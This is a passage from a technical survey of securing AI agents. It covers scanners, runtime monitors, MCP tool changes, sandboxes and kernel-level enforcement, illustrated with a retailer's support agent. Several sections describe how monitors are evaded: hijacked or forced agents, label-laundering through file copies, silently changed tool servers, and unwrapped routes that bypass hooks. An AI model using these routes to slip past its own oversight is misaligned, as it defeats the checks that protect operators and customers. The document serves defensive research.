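That exception applies to most of the agent systems covered so far. A monitor such as Progent receives tool calls but not the tools' source code, while a scanner has the source code but no tickets. The ranking therefore doesn't apply to agents, and the theorem is no reason for a company to drop its scanner once it has a monitor.

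The model also allows executions that never end. Real agents do stop, so a checker could in theory go through all their executions, but with 10⁵⁰⁰ possible replies at a single step, this is impossible in practice.

### Monitors that hold actions back

Schneider's limit applies to monitors that can only halt the program. *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2005) studies edit automata, which can also suppress a program's actions or insert new ones. The paper requires a monitor to be sound, so that its output always obeys the policy, and transparent, so that it preserves the meaning of executions that already obeyed it.

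An edit automaton can withhold a program's actions while the program continues as if they had been carried out, then release them all if the series turns out to be valid. This lets it enforce what Ligatti and colleagues call infinite renewal properties, in which an infinite execution is valid exactly when it has infinitely many valid prefixes. These include every safety property and some liveness properties, such as the requirement that a program that does anything must eventually write an audit record. The automaton enforces this requirement by withholding every action until the program writes the record.

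A monitor that holds back actions may still be unable to enforce the rule "the agent eventually closes every ticket it opens". If the agent always opens a new ticket before it closes the last one, it may eventually close each ticket, but they are never all closed at once. The monitor therefore never reaches a point at which it can safely release the actions it has held.

Tool calls are hard to hold back in this way. If the monitor delays `query_orders`, the model has no rows to use in its reply. Ligatti and colleagues acknowledge that a monitor can't pretend to send an email, wait for the response and then decide not to send it.

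Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, proves a version of Schneider's result for agents whose actions are irreversible. A monitor that allows or blocks each call before it runs can enforce exactly the safety properties it can recognise, except a policy that no execution satisfies. Edit automata can enforce more. In Ray's example, the monitor can't enforce a rule that a confirmation must eventually follow every payment. If it allows a payment, it can't take the money back when no confirmation comes, but blocking the payment would stop an agent that was about to confirm. A programmer might avoid the problem by combining payment and confirmation in one tool, which amounts to rewriting the program.

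Ray's result assumes that the monitor can evaluate its conditions correctly. This assumption is reasonable when the monitor compares two email addresses. But deciding whether a message contains personal data requires judgement, and if a language model makes that judgement, the guarantee holds only when the model is right.

The halting problem also limits advance analysis of the policy. Ray proves that if a policy language has two counters that can rise, fall and be compared with zero, no procedure can always determine whether a policy forbids anything. The analysis is possible in a more restricted language whose counters only rise, which is enough to express a daily spending cap. Designers who want to check a policy before enforcing it therefore have a reason to keep its language simple.

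### How often the limits matter

These theorems establish what no scanner or monitor can do for every program or policy. They don't give the error rate of any real tool, because a scanner that misjudges infinitely many programs could still be right about every agent a company builds.

Pérez-Acle's simulations show how wide this gap can be. Of 2.2 million randomly generated programs, 1.6% were unsafe. Among the longest programs, a test that ran each one for eight steps missed 30.2% of the unsafe ones, but tests of 128 steps or more missed none, regardless of program length. By contrast, when Pérez-Acle tried eight checkers, each against a program designed to contradict it, only the one that ran the program for the full time limit was ever right.

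Neither simulation used agent code, so the percentages don't apply to products such as Agent Audit. Still, the contrast suggests that who wrote the code matters. The retailer's own programmers have no reason to write functions that fool the scanner, so the worst case in the theorems may rarely occur in their work. The author of a malicious MCP server wants to fool the scanner, and can test one version after another against any that is publicly available.

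## Tools and code that do not exist when the scan is run

A scanner can read only what exists when it runs. For an agent, according to *Agents as Software* (2026), that includes its prompts, tool schemas, policies, memory and retrieval settings, and workflow structure. After the scan, the model chooses arguments for tools the scanner has already read. An MCP server can add tools or change existing ones. The model also writes shell commands and whole programs, and some agents install new tools or write their own. What the scanner and the monitor miss differs in each of these cases.

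### Arguments for a tool the scanner has read

When the retailer scans the support agent, the `send_email` tool exists but the recipient's address has not been set. The scanner can still determine what inputs each tool accepts, but the monitor has to check the actual values at run time. For example, the scanner can establish that `run_python` accepts any program, while the repaired `query_orders` accepts only a customer number.

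Neither the scanner nor the monitor can determine whether a permitted value is the right one. Suppose the retailer adds a refund tool with a limit of £50, and a customer falsely reports a broken vase. The scanner passes the tool because its limit is sensible, and the monitor allows a £40 refund because it is within the limit and goes to the customer who opened the ticket. Detecting the false claim would require checking another record, such as the courier's photograph of the parcel.

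The scanner and monitor work well together here because the list of tools is fixed and the retailer has the code for each one. When an agent gets its tools from someone else's server, the list can change and the agent's operator doesn't have the tools' code.

### Tools that arrive or change on a server

Suppose `query_orders` now runs on an outside company's MCP server. A scan of the server's tool list may soon be out of date, because the current Model Context Protocol specification allows the list to change over time. The list may also depend on the caller's authorisation, but it must not differ between connections or change as a side effect of other requests on the same connection. Model Context Protocol (2026) lists the ban on differences between connections as a change from the November 2025 version. This change makes scanning a little more reliable, since a scanner that uses the agent's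 own credentials should now get the list the agent would get at that moment.

According to Model Context Protocol's *Subscriptions* (2026), a client that wants to be notified when a server's list of tools changes has to open a `subscriptions/listen` stream and request `toolsListChanged` notices. The server must not send notices that the client hasn't requested. Even when the client has subscribed, the server only "should" send one, which is weaker than "must". The notice doesn't include the change itself, so the client has to fetch the list again and compare it with the previous one.

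The rules on list changes don't require anyone to approve a changed tool. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, reported in March that clients did not alert users when a tool's definition changed. Some clients also ignore notices that the list has changed. In *MCP*, a thread on the forum of the coding tool Cursor, users complain that its command-line version does nothing when the list changes during a session. They want new tools for ordinary reasons. For example, some servers offer more tools after the user logs in, and a client that refused every change would break these servers.

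MCP servers often change after they are registered. *Same Name, Different Server* (Kraishan, 2026) compared successive versions of the 8,900 servers, out of 21,643 in the public MCP registry, that had more than one version. Just over half had changed their description, packages or network address, and 40.6% had made at least one silent change, in which the meaning or destination changed but the identifiers stayed the same. Most of those servers had reworded a description, which is often harmless. However, 370 servers (4.2%) had moved to a different host under the same name. Kraishan thinks most of these moves were routine, but neither the registry nor a client can tell a routine move from a takeover. The count leaves out changes to the tools themselves, because the registry doesn't record tool definitions.

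Among the servers that changed, the median time to the first change was less than a day, so a review done at installation could be out of date the same day.

One defense is pinning, in which the client stores a fingerprint of whatever the user approved and raises an alarm if the fingerprint no longer matches. Kraishan recommends pinning packages and host addresses. *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly* (2026), which followed a registry for 89 days, recommends tying each approval to the exact content of the description and regularly rechecking every server. Rechecking mainly the servers with a history of changes would miss too many of the others.

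A fingerprint of a tool's definition can't reveal a change in the tool's behaviour. *ProbeID* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) repeatedly tested 59 tools from 16 published servers over eleven weeks, with the version numbers pinned, and seven of the tools began to give different responses. That doesn't make them malicious, but it does show that pinning a version number doesn't guarantee the same behaviour.

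One remedy is to record a tool's responses to a set of test inputs when the user first approves it, then repeat a secret selection of those tests before later use. In a trial with 16 tasks and tools that had been swapped for faulty copies, this cut the number of tasks with corrupted data from 15 to 9. Two of the faulty tools always passed because they responded to every stored input as the originals had. The method is also awkward for a tool such as `send_email`, since testing it means sending emails.

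A monitor with an allowlist, such as Progent, blocks a new tool until somebody writes a rule for it. A changed tool is harder to catch, because its calls may have the same name and the same kind of arguments as before. If the outside server returned the right orders but also kept a copy of every customer number, the fingerprint and the test responses would still match, and the monitor would allow each call. The retailer could avoid this by running a pinned copy of the server's code on its own machines, with no access to the internet. The scanner could then read the code that handles the calls.

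New tools can also be dangerous in combination even if each is safe alone. A Model Context Protocol blog post (2026) notes that users routinely combine tools from several servers in one session, so the risk depends on the whole session rather than on any single server. One server might supply private data and another a way to send it out, and a scanner that examined each separately could pass both. The client could rerun the policy analysis whenever its tool list changed. Agenra's checks are fast enough for that, but the analysis requires knowing what the new tool can do. A server can describe this in its tool annotations, but under the specification, clients are not to trust annotations from servers they don't trust. It is safest to assume that a new tool can do anything until someone has examined its code.

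Some of AgentFlow's misses came from developers' own code that attached tools at run time, even without MCP.

### Commands and programs that the model writes

The scanner can often give the retailer more useful information by reading the settings of the sandbox where the code runs than by reporting that `run_python` accepts any program. If the sandbox has no network connection and holds no customer data, no program the model writes can send the customer list to an outside server. If it has both, the retailer needs some way to judge each program.

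A monitor placed at the tool call receives the program's text, so it has to predict what the program will do, as a scanner does, but while a user waits. *CARE* (2026) presents such a monitor for shell commands. It rewrites each command into a standard form, applies fast static checks, and allows it, warns about it or refuses it. Only the unclear cases go to a further stage. CARE judges each command in isolation, with no record of earlier ones.

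*Tether*, a November 2026 paper by researchers at Google DeepMind and elsewhere, describes a system that instead runs the command first and then decides whether to keep the results.

### How Tether judges a command

The command runs in a disposable layer over the file system. It can read the real files, but its writes go into the layer, and a local proxy holds back its network requests. As the command runs, Tether records its system calls, which are the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file, write to one or connect to another machine.

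Tether translates these calls into 11 types of action, including read, copy and upload. It checks each action against the policy and updates the labels that record how sensitive each file is. When a command copies a file, the copy takes on the original's label. When file contents reach the model, Tether also attaches the file's label to the agent's context, much as in FIDES. If the policy permits every action, Tether commits the changes to the real file system; otherwise, it discards the layer.

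The researchers illustrate this with an agent that may read a sensitive inventory, `servers.csv`, and may upload a harmless status report to GitHub. It runs three commands:

| Command | Label on `report.txt` beforehand | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| Upload `report.txt` | Public | Allow |
| Copy `servers.csv` over `report.txt` | Public | Allow, and relabel `report.txt` as Sensitive |
| Upload `report.txt` | Sensitive | Refuse |

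The two upload commands are identical, so a monitor that checks each command in isolation would either block the harmless report or allow the inventory to be uploaded. Tether's label also follows the data through any number of intermediate files. Because the copy never passes through the model, the label doesn't spread to the agent's context, and the agent can keep uploading other public files. A simple history rule that banned uploads after any contact with the inventory would block those uploads too.

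System calls show which files a program read and wrote, but not which data went where. If a program reads one file and then writes another, Tether assumes the second contains data from the first. This is the same over-approximation the scanner makes, applied to a single run.

Tether can't hold network requests until the program finishes, because a program often needs the reply before it can continue. It therefore decides whether to forward each request based on the actions it has observed so far. It can still discard the program's file changes later, but it can't recall a request it has forwarded.

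The policy in the experiments had 24 rules. The researchers proved in Lean that it upholds seven properties, including that secret data never leaves the local machine. The proofs assume that Tether has inferred the actions correctly. The researchers tested this assumption by generating random chains of file operations and by telling an agent to get past the monitor. The agent succeeded in 40% of attempts against an early version and in none after two rounds of repairs.

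### Tether against a model-based monitor

The researchers replayed recorded runs from two benchmarks, MonitoringBenchHonest (system administration) and LinuxArena (software engineering). In some runs the agent did only its assigned job, and in others it also pursued a harmful side task. They compared Tether with the auto mode of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Auto mode uses a language model to review proposed actions, and the researchers tested it with its default rules and again with Tether's policy added to its instructions.

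| | Tether | Auto mode, default | Auto mode with Tether's policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful runs blocked (of 344) | 344 (100%) | 315 (91.6%) | 307 (89.2%) |
| Benign runs refused (of 1,590) | 74 (4.7%) | 155 (9.7%) | 55 (3.5%) |

By default, auto mode often blocked edits that the task explicitly allowed. Adding the policy prevented many of these errors, but the model then applied the list of approved network addresses inconsistently and missed more harmful runs. With or without the policy, it failed to detect harm inside scripts because the command that starts a script doesn't show what the script will do. It could also give different verdicts on the same run.

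The results differed widely between the benchmarks, which the totals don't show. On MonitoringBenchHonest, auto mode with the policy missed 35 of 199 harmful runs and refused 14.7% of benign ones, while Tether missed none and refused 2.3%. On LinuxArena, auto mode with the policy missed two of 145 harmful runs and refused 1.7% of benign ones, compared with Tether's 5.0%. A company that can tolerate an occasional miss might prefer auto mode for work like LinuxArena's.

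Most of Tether's 74 refusals of benign runs were correct under its policy. In 57 of them, the agent had tried to edit a protected file or contact an outside machine when its task hadn't asked for either. The other 17 are more clearly errors and amount to 1.1% of benign runs. They involved reads of secret or sensitive files, often by searches that open every file in a folder.

A company's first policy for its own agents would probably fall short of the perfect score, because the policy that earned it was revised using runs from the benchmarks. A language model wrote the first draft, and the researchers revised it until it kept the seven properties without blocking too much ordinary work. They took the labels and lists of permitted addresses from each task's description and used no information about the harmful side tasks.

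The 344 harmful runs also include only those that Tether could follow from beginning to end. It can't trace processes that continue in the background after a command has finished, or follow data inside a database. It can detect these operations and either refuse them or ask a person. The researchers estimate that this would let it intercept another 36.3% of runs on MonitoringBenchHonest and 71.5% on LinuxArena. But refusing all database operations would make the support agent useless, because it has to look up orders for every ticket.

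A further 28.2% and 22.1% of runs on the two benchmarks require someone to judge the content of the agent's work. A good edit and a bad edit to the same file can produce the same system calls, so a monitor that relies on those calls can't tell them apart. A scanner run before deployment can't check the edit either, because it doesn't exist yet. For these cases, the researchers suggest pairing Tether with a language model that can read the edit, although the guarantee would then depend on the model's judgement.

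### Checking generated code just before it runs

A static analyser can examine a program that the model writes after it is written and before it runs. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) presents an agent system called Elba that uses this approach. Elba's agents act by writing programs in Haskell, whose type checker determines before a program runs what kinds of data it handles and what effects it can have on the outside world.

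The developer gives Elba a prompt, a set of functions that the model may use, and the type that the finished program must have. The model writes a program. If the type checker rejects it, Elba returns the error and the model tries again. Only a program that passes can run.

For the support agent, the retailer might supply these two functions:

```haskell
ticketAddress :: TicketId -> SupportIO (Trusted Address)
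sendEmail     :: Trusted Address -> Text -> SupportIO ()
```

The first function takes a ticket number and returns a trusted address. The second takes a trusted address and a message, and sends the email. Only the retailer's library can create a `Trusted Address`, so the type checker rejects a program that tries to email `drop@example.net`, because that address is plain text. `SupportIO` covers the outside effects the retailer permits. A program that tried to open its own network connection would have a different type, and Elba would reject that too.

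The check covers every branch of the program, including one that would run only on the last day of the month, while Tether observes only the branch that runs. But these two types leave gaps. The model could look up the address on someone else's ticket, or email the customer list to the stranger who opened ticket 4812, whose address the library treats as trusted.

Closing the second gap requires tracking where the message came from, and the static approach does this partly at run time, as a monitor does. Zhou and colleagues use LIO, an existing Haskell library that labels data. The type checker ensures that the program uses LIO for every action, but LIO compares the labels while the program runs and stops it if the data is not allowed to go to the recipient. Elba's file library also checks some paths at run time, because the code may not show a file's true location.

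An agent usually has to read something before it can decide what to do next, so Elba lets a generated program call the model again. The program that this call generates must satisfy the same type as the program that made the call, or a stricter type, so a hijacked model can't gain permissions by delegating to another agent.

Zhou and colleagues tested Elba on the Slack part of AgentDojo. All four models resisted all 105 standard attacks without a policy, so the researchers couldn't use those attacks to measure Elba's protection. They instead simulated the worst case by forcing the model to follow the attacker's instructions. Without a policy, between 16% and 42% of the attacks then succeeded, depending on the model. With a policy, no attacks succeeded in 735 runs per model.

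Under these forced attacks, the perfect score came with a large drop in task completion, from between 67% and 76% to between 40% and 48%. Elba still completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL when both enforced policies. The policy in this test relied on LIO's labels, so the perfect score is evidence for static and run-time checks together, not for type checking alone.

Other designs use Scala, another typed language. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) compiles the agent's code in a safe mode that forbids type casts and reflection, which a program could use to hide what it has access to. Reflection has long made ordinary software hard to scan, but a language for agents can leave it out. *LACUNA* (2026) inserts checked code into a program that is already running. Its design should work in any typed language that tracks effects and can recompile code at run time, which excludes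 the shell and ordinary Python.

A restricted language can also make the analyser very small. DeepClause's *Static taint analysis for LLM agents* describes a tool that turns a plain-language description of an agent into a program in a language based on Prolog. Before the program runs, an analyser of about 200 lines traces untrusted data through it. The analyser treats user input, outside parameters and all model output as sources. Tools that run code are the most serious sinks, followed by the system prompt, which holds the standing instructions that the model reads first.

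The analyser examines each clause of the program separately, so it can miss data passed between clauses. It also can't recognise code that makes a value safe, so a programmer who fixes a problem may still get the warning. A milder warning appears whenever the model works with untrusted text in its conversation. Almost every support agent does that, so the retailer would learn little from this warning. DeepClause can check the program that organises the agent's work, but it can't predict code that the model writes later for a tool like `run_python`. It can only warn that untrusted code may reach the tool.

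*Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (2026) avoids the problem much as CaMeL does, by having the model write the whole program before it reads any website. Of 627 programs that its system, Baya, generated, only 13 contained a further call to a model, and that model had no tools. Like CaMeL, the approach has difficulty with ticket 4812, because the agent must read the ticket before it can plan the work.

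These languages help more if the agent can do its whole job in one. The support agent probably could, with a handful of functions for tickets, orders and email. A coding agent needs compilers, package managers and thousands of other programs that weren't written in typed Haskell. A monitor such as Tether can run those programs unchanged.

### Tools that the agent adds for itself

Some agents might save a useful script as a new tool, or download a skill, and use it in every later session. A bad skill can do more harm than a bad program that runs once, because it can influence hundreds of later tasks.

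The scan before deployment can't examine a skill that the agent will download next month, but it can check whether any of the agent's tools could add one, either by writing to the folder from which the agent loads its skills or by running a package installer. The retailer's original agent might be able to do both through `run_python`. If the agent doesn't need new skills, the retailer can make the folder read-only.

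Where an agent does need them, the company can scan each skill when it arrives. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) proposes to compute the largest set of effects that a skill's scripts could have, then compare it with the permissions the skill declares:

```text
actual effects ⊆ computed effects ⊆ declared permissions
```

The analyser does this by running the script on summaries of values instead of real ones. For example, a skill might declare that it writes only to a `reports` folder, while its script takes the file's location from the model. The analyser has to summarise the location as "any path", which is broader than the declaration allows, so the skill fails the check. It would fail even if the model always chose the right folder. Sound analyses usually produce some false alarms like this.

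A monitor receives the installation as a command or a file write, and later receives each call the new tool makes. The two events may be weeks apart, so a monitor that keeps no data between sessions can't connect them. Labels like Tether's could help if the monitor saved them between sessions. A script that the agent wrote after reading a stranger's ticket would still carry the label "untrusted", and the monitor could block it from being loaded as a skill.

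The instructions in a skill are harder to check than its scripts. Suppose a downloaded skill tells the agent to offer a full refund whenever a customer mentions a lawyer. The scanner finds no dangerous code, and the monitor allows each refund because it is within the limit and goes to the right customer. Neither can detect that the retailer never wanted this rule. The skill still can't raise the refund limit as long as the agent can't edit the monitor's policy.

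## Whether a runtime monitor sees every action

A monitor can block only the actions that reach it. Anderson required a monitor to check every access, a property known as complete mediation. Whether an agent's monitor does this depends mostly on where developers put the check. They can put it inside the agent's process (the running program that contains the agent loop), in a proxy between the agent and its tool servers, or in the operating system and network underneath.

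```text
  agent's process                         tool server
┌─────────────────────────┐             ┌───────────────┐
│ model's call ─► (hook)  │─► (proxy) ─►│ tool function │
└─────────────────────────┘             └───────────────┘
┌───────────────────────────────────────────────────────┐
│ operating system and network (monitor)                │
└───────────────────────────────────────────────────────┘
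```

Two of the support agent's tools behave very differently under these arrangements. `send_email` connects to the company's mail provider and hands over a message. `run_python` starts a separate program. Suppose the model uses it to work out a refund in euros:

```python
import refunds
print(refunds.total(ticket=4812, currency="EUR"))
```

The retailer's programmers wrote `refunds`, which reads a price file, fetches an exchange rate from a website and adds a line to a log. None of those operations appears in the two lines the model wrote.

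### What agent frameworks check by default

*Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examines the public source code of three agent frameworks to find out what they already check before running a tool. Two of them, LangChain (with its companion LangGraph) and LlamaIndex, are general libraries for building agents. The third, the Stripe Agent Toolkit, connects agents to Stripe's payment services.

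LangChain and LlamaIndex look up a tool's name in the list the developer supplied. LangChain usually also checks that the arguments have the right form. Stripe's toolkit restricts the agent to a list of permitted actions, and a developer can limit the permissions of the access key it uses. Mellafe Zuvic calls these checks capability gates because they determine which tools an agent can use.

By default, none of the three checks whether the values in a particular call are allowed. If the retailer relied on such a gate, an email to `drop@example.net` would pass because the tool exists and the address is valid text. In Stripe's toolkit, the unchecked values include the amount and the customer. Developers can add human approval in LangChain and LlamaIndex, but they have to build it in themselves.

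Mellafe Zuvic confirmed the gap by giving LangChain a fixed tool call that redirected a merchant's payouts to an attacker's account. LangChain ran it against a simulated payment system. Mellafe Zuvic's checker, ScopeGate, refused the same call because the account wasn't on the operator's list. ScopeGate also refused all 48 forbidden calls in a prepared set. Another model attempted 29 forbidden calls over 40 rounds, using the reasons for earlier refusals, and ScopeGate refused all of them. The tests exposed a flaw in an early version that let an invalid payment through, and Mellafe Zuvic fixed it.

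The gap matters more for some models than for others. In a companion test of 27 models, planted text presented a forbidden action as part of the user's task. On average, cheaper models attempted the action 60% of the time and flagship models 19%. A company that picks a cheap model for a busy support desk may therefore need the check most. These rates come from one researcher's set of attacks and measure attempts, not successful thefts.

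The audit covers particular versions of public code, so Stripe's own servers may check more. Mellafe Zuvic doesn't call the gap a vulnerability in the frameworks, which leave this check to the developer. The paper also claims that ScopeGate would work equally well inside the application, in a local proxy or at a central gateway, as long as every call with side effects passes through it. The hard part is making sure that every such call does. Mellafe Zuvic tested ScopeGate only inside the application, so the claims about the proxy and the gateway rest on its design.

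### A hook in the agent's process

*AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) provides hooks for 14 agent frameworks in Python, JavaScript and Go. A hook is code that runs automatically before some event, here a tool call. A Python developer adds two lines of code, and AEGIS modifies the libraries the agent uses to communicate with its model. When the model's reply contains a tool call, the hook pauses the agent and sends the tool's name and arguments to a separate gateway. The gateway searches the text for 22 suspicious patterns and applies the company's policy. It then allows the call, blocks it or holds it for a person to review.

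When an agent calls `send_email`, the gateway receives the recipient and the whole message before any encryption. In one published example, the gateway holds an email for approval that contains a social security number and a card number. It also lists an email address as personal data, although the only address in the call is the recipient's. If an address alone were enough to hold a call, a person would have to approve every email the support agent sent.

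When the model calls `run_python`, the gateway receives the two lines of code the model wrote. It can search them for patterns, but `refunds` runs after the gateway has responded.

AEGIS blocked all 48 attacks in a set that its developers compiled from known techniques, and wrongly flagged 6 of 500 harmless calls. Those results measure how well the gateway judges the calls it receives, not how many calls could miss the hook. Yuan and colleagues exclude any call made outside the libraries they modify. If the retailer had a nightly job that called `send_email` directly to send receipts, AEGIS wouldn't check those emails. *Stop Means Stop* (2026) notes that a single unwrapped route to a tool is enough to bypass any wrapper's check.

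The hook also runs in the same process as the agent's other code, so the retailer has to trust every library loaded there not to interfere with it. This is a good reason to run the model's programs in a separate process, as `run_python` does here.

Coding agents can have hooks too. Grasso's *Introducing Prempti* describes a tool from the Falco project that adds one to Claude Code. Falco is open-source software that monitors Linux machines and containers for security problems. Before each tool call, Prempti's hook sends the request to a local Falco service, which checks it against a set of rules and returns "allow", "deny" or "ask". By default, Prempti denies access to files that hold keys and passwords, and asks the user about some file access outside the project's folder.

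Like AEGIS, Prempti doesn't monitor what a program does after the agent starts it. Falco's rules receive the command but not the program's system calls. Grasso recommends Falco's kernel monitoring for those calls, and warns that Prempti is not a sandbox and that an agent might find a route the hook doesn't cover. Prempti also runs under the user's own account, according to Falco's *Guardrails and Observability for AI Coding Agents*. A coding agent often runs under the same account, and then ordinary file permissions won't protect the monitor from the agent. That makes it harder to meet Anderson's requirement that a monitor be tamper-proof.

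If a hook is missing, the call runs without a warning. Prempti has a health command that sends an artificial event and checks that the answer is "allow". This confirms that requests reach Falco and answers come back. But a service with no rules loaded would presumably give the same answer, so users should also try a call that their rules forbid.

### A proxy in front of the tool servers

If the retailer moves its tools to an MCP server, a proxy can check each request before it reaches the server. Microsoft offers an open-source option, the Agent Governance Toolkit, which was still in public preview in April 2026. It scans tool descriptions for hidden instructions before the model receives them, checks each call against a policy, and inspects the server's response before returning it to the agent.

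The proxy receives the recipient and body of each `send_email` call, just as a hook does. If it runs separately, faulty code in the agent's process can't disable it. But according to *Agent Governance Toolkit* (mosiddi, 2026), developers can also call the toolkit's policy engine from the agent's own code. The engine then has the weaknesses of a hook. To keep it separate, they have to run it as a sidecar, a second container next to the agent's.

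A proxy covers only the tools behind it. If `send_email` stayed in the agent's code as an ordinary function, its messages would go straight to the mail provider. The retailer could prevent this by giving the mail password only to the tool server and having that server accept connections only from the proxy. The agent could then send company email only through the proxy.

The refund program shows how little of `run_python` a proxy covers:

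| Event | What the proxy receives | What an operating-system monitor can record |
|---|---|---|
| The model calls `run_python` | The tool's name and two lines of code | The start of a Python process |
| `refunds` reads the price file | Nothing | The file's name |
| `refunds` fetches the exchange rate | Nothing | The network address it contacts |
| `refunds` writes to the log | Nothing | The file's name |
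| The tool returns its answer | The refund total | Data sent over a connection |

The proxy is on the connection between the agent and the tool server. When `refunds` opens a file or contacts a website, the Python process sends the request to the tool server's operating system, so the request doesn't pass through the proxy. Only the program's output does, and here that is a single number, which would be the same if `refunds` had also read the customer list. A stricter policy doesn't solve this, because the proxy never receives the operations the policy would apply to.

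The retailer also has to trust the tool server, which might do more than the call requests. Microsoft's *Agent Governance Toolkit Threat Model* lists tools that behave unsafely within their permitted scope as a remaining risk. The toolkit also checks each call separately, according to Microsoft's *Known Limitations & Design Boundaries*, so it can't apply the rule that blocks email once the agent has read other customers' rows.

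If a proxy is the only route to the tools and it crashes, the agent stops working, but no unchecked call gets through. Microsoft's policy engine also refuses a call if it hits an error while evaluating the rules. Configuration mistakes are more dangerous. If nobody has loaded a policy, the default is to allow everything, and the toolkit's dashboard may still show the agent as "governed". For production, Microsoft recommends a strict mode that refuses any call that no rule allows.

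### The operating system and the network

A program must go through the kernel, the core of the operating system, to open a file or a network connection. A monitor there can therefore check what both `refunds` and the model's code do. Tether works at this level when it traces system calls.

*ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) enforces rules in the Linux kernel with eBPF, a feature that lets administrators run small, pre-checked programs there. The rules apply to the agent's process and every process it starts. A privileged program loads the company's rules before the agent starts. The agent can add its own rules later, but they can't weaken the company's.

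Zheng and colleagues report that ActPlane resolved 2.0 to 3.2 times more policy violations than four alternatives, including FIDES, which works on tool calls. Besides having wider coverage, ActPlane tells the agent why it refused an action, so some of its lead probably comes from agents correcting themselves. One of the alternatives was also a kernel monitor, but it gave no explanation for its refusals. On a separate set of 361 personal-assistant tasks, ActPlane prevented 74% of the unsafe behaviour that occurred without it.

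A kernel monitor is much less useful for `send_email`. The mail library normally encrypts the message before it reaches the kernel, so the monitor can record only that a process connected to the mail provider and sent some data. A reply to a customer and a message to a stranger look the same, because both go to the provider's server first. The monitor therefore can't enforce the retailer's rule that email may go only to the ticket's customer.

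Many other rules have the same problem. Zheng and colleagues collected 1,361 rules from the instruction files that developers wrote for coding agents in 64 popular projects. A monitor could decide 45% of them from single operating-system events or sequences of events. Another 38% required reading the contents of files. The remaining 17% concerned matters such as how the agent should explain its reasoning. Most of the rules therefore need information that ActPlane doesn't use.

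A network proxy can recover some of the missing information by decrypting traffic. *AgentBouncer* (2026) describes a system in which the kernel passes system calls to a monitor before carrying them out, while a separate proxy decrypts web requests and reads their addresses and contents. For other connections, the language model that decides what to allow receives only the destination's name and port number. The proxy could therefore read the recipient of an email sent through a provider's web interface, but not of one sent over an ordinary mail connection. The proxy's operator must protect it well, because it can read every password and customer record that passes through it.

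*AgentSight* (2025) reads the encrypted traffic between the agent and its model, records kernel events, and matches the two, so an investigator can trace a file access back to the model's reply that led to it. It observes agents but doesn't block their actions.

An operating-system monitor covers only the machine it runs on. If `run_python` runs on another company's server, the retailer's kernel handles the connection to that server but none of the program's file operations. If the model's vendor runs the tool, as Anthropic does with web search, none of the retailer's monitors can check a call beforehand. *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)* (Errico, 2026) includes vendor integration as a fourth place for a monitor, alongside gateways, hooks and the kernel. AARM is a specification, so its statements about how well each place would work are design claims.

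The company also has to trust the kernel, the monitor's code and the rules loaded into it. ActPlane's guarantee covers only the events someone has configured it to intercept, so leaving an event out of the configuration has the same effect as a missing hook. Cutting off the network is simpler, but *Stop Means Stop* notes that this does not cover files or shared memory.

*Stop Means Stop* ranks kernel checks first, network isolation second, and wrappers last, to be used only where the operating system can't enforce the rule. That order makes sense for preventing bypasses, but the support agent needs more than one kind of check. A hook or tool proxy can compare the recipient of each email with the ticket, and the operating system can restrict `run_python` to the price file, the log and the exchange-rate website. *ContractWarden* (2026) supports this combination and notes that systems such as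 Progent and FIDES have more information about an agent's actions and can complement a kernel monitor.

### How much delay the checks add

| System | Reported delay | What the measurement covers |
|---|---|---|
| AEGIS | 8.3 ms per call (median), 23.1 ms at the 99th percentile | Hook, trip to a local gateway, and decision |
| Microsoft's toolkit | 0.07 ms per action (median), 0.42 ms at the 99th percentile | Policy, trust and permission checks and logging, in one process |
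| ActPlane | 1.9% on agent tasks, up to 8.4% when compiling a kernel | Enforcement in the operating system |
| AgentSight | Under 3% | Observation only |

The tests of AEGIS and Microsoft's toolkit measured different things, so their results, which make AEGIS look about 120 times slower, are not directly comparable. Microsoft's *Governance Overhead Benchmark* (2026) excluded all network traffic, so its figure is for a check inside the agent's process, not for a proxy. Writing a tamper-evident log accounts for about two-thirds of that small delay. For agents that communicate across several machines, Microsoft expects 5 to 50 ms per interaction. Grasso gives no figure for Prempti.

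Delay is a weak reason to prefer one place for the monitor over another, because Microsoft estimates that a call to a model typically takes 200 to 2,000 ms. Human approval takes much longer. AEGIS checks for a reviewer's answer every two seconds and waits up to five minutes, during which the customer's ticket makes no progress.

### Finding the routes that miss the monitor

Developers can easily overestimate how much their monitor covers. *Governed MCP* (2026) withdraws an earlier claim by the developer of Anima OS, an operating system that runs agents, that all 123 routes from an agent to the system passed through the monitor. A new count on a running machine found 59 routes, of which the monitor covered 43. The monitor covered all tool calls and all functions the system offers to agents, but six routes through system calls still had no check.

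A scanner can help find such gaps before deployment. *Stop Means Stop* describes one that searches an agent's code for direct calls to dangerous functions that skip the wrapper. It would probably find the retailer's nightly job, because the code calls `send_email` by name. It can't reliably find calls that the program chooses while running, or calls inside other companies' libraries. Used this way, the scanner only has to check whether calls to dangerous functions go through the monitor, which is much easier than predicting what the model will do.

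The same kind of check applies to the boundary around an agent. In September 2026, Anthropic described four incidents in which testers told models they were in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the models connected to the real internet. Anthropic believes the incidents would not have happened if the test environments had been isolated as intended.

A configuration check before the run would probably have caught the open internet connection, though this is an inference. *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (Anthropic, 2026) attributes the connection to a misunderstanding between Anthropic and the company that built the environments. A scanner that read only Anthropic's settings might therefore have found nothing wrong. A more reliable check would try to reach the internet from inside the environment and cancel the run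 if it succeeded. Anthropic thinks carefully validating every internet route beforehand would have helped reveal the problem sooner.

Anthropic now asks outside testers to verify that the test environment is isolated before every evaluation (*Improving our alignment and security efforts*, 2026). A connection could still open after that check, so Anthropic has also added a runtime monitor to its own evaluations. If a model unexpectedly gains internet access, the monitor blocks the tool call, ends the task and alerts a person.

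## False alarms and misses, and what they cost

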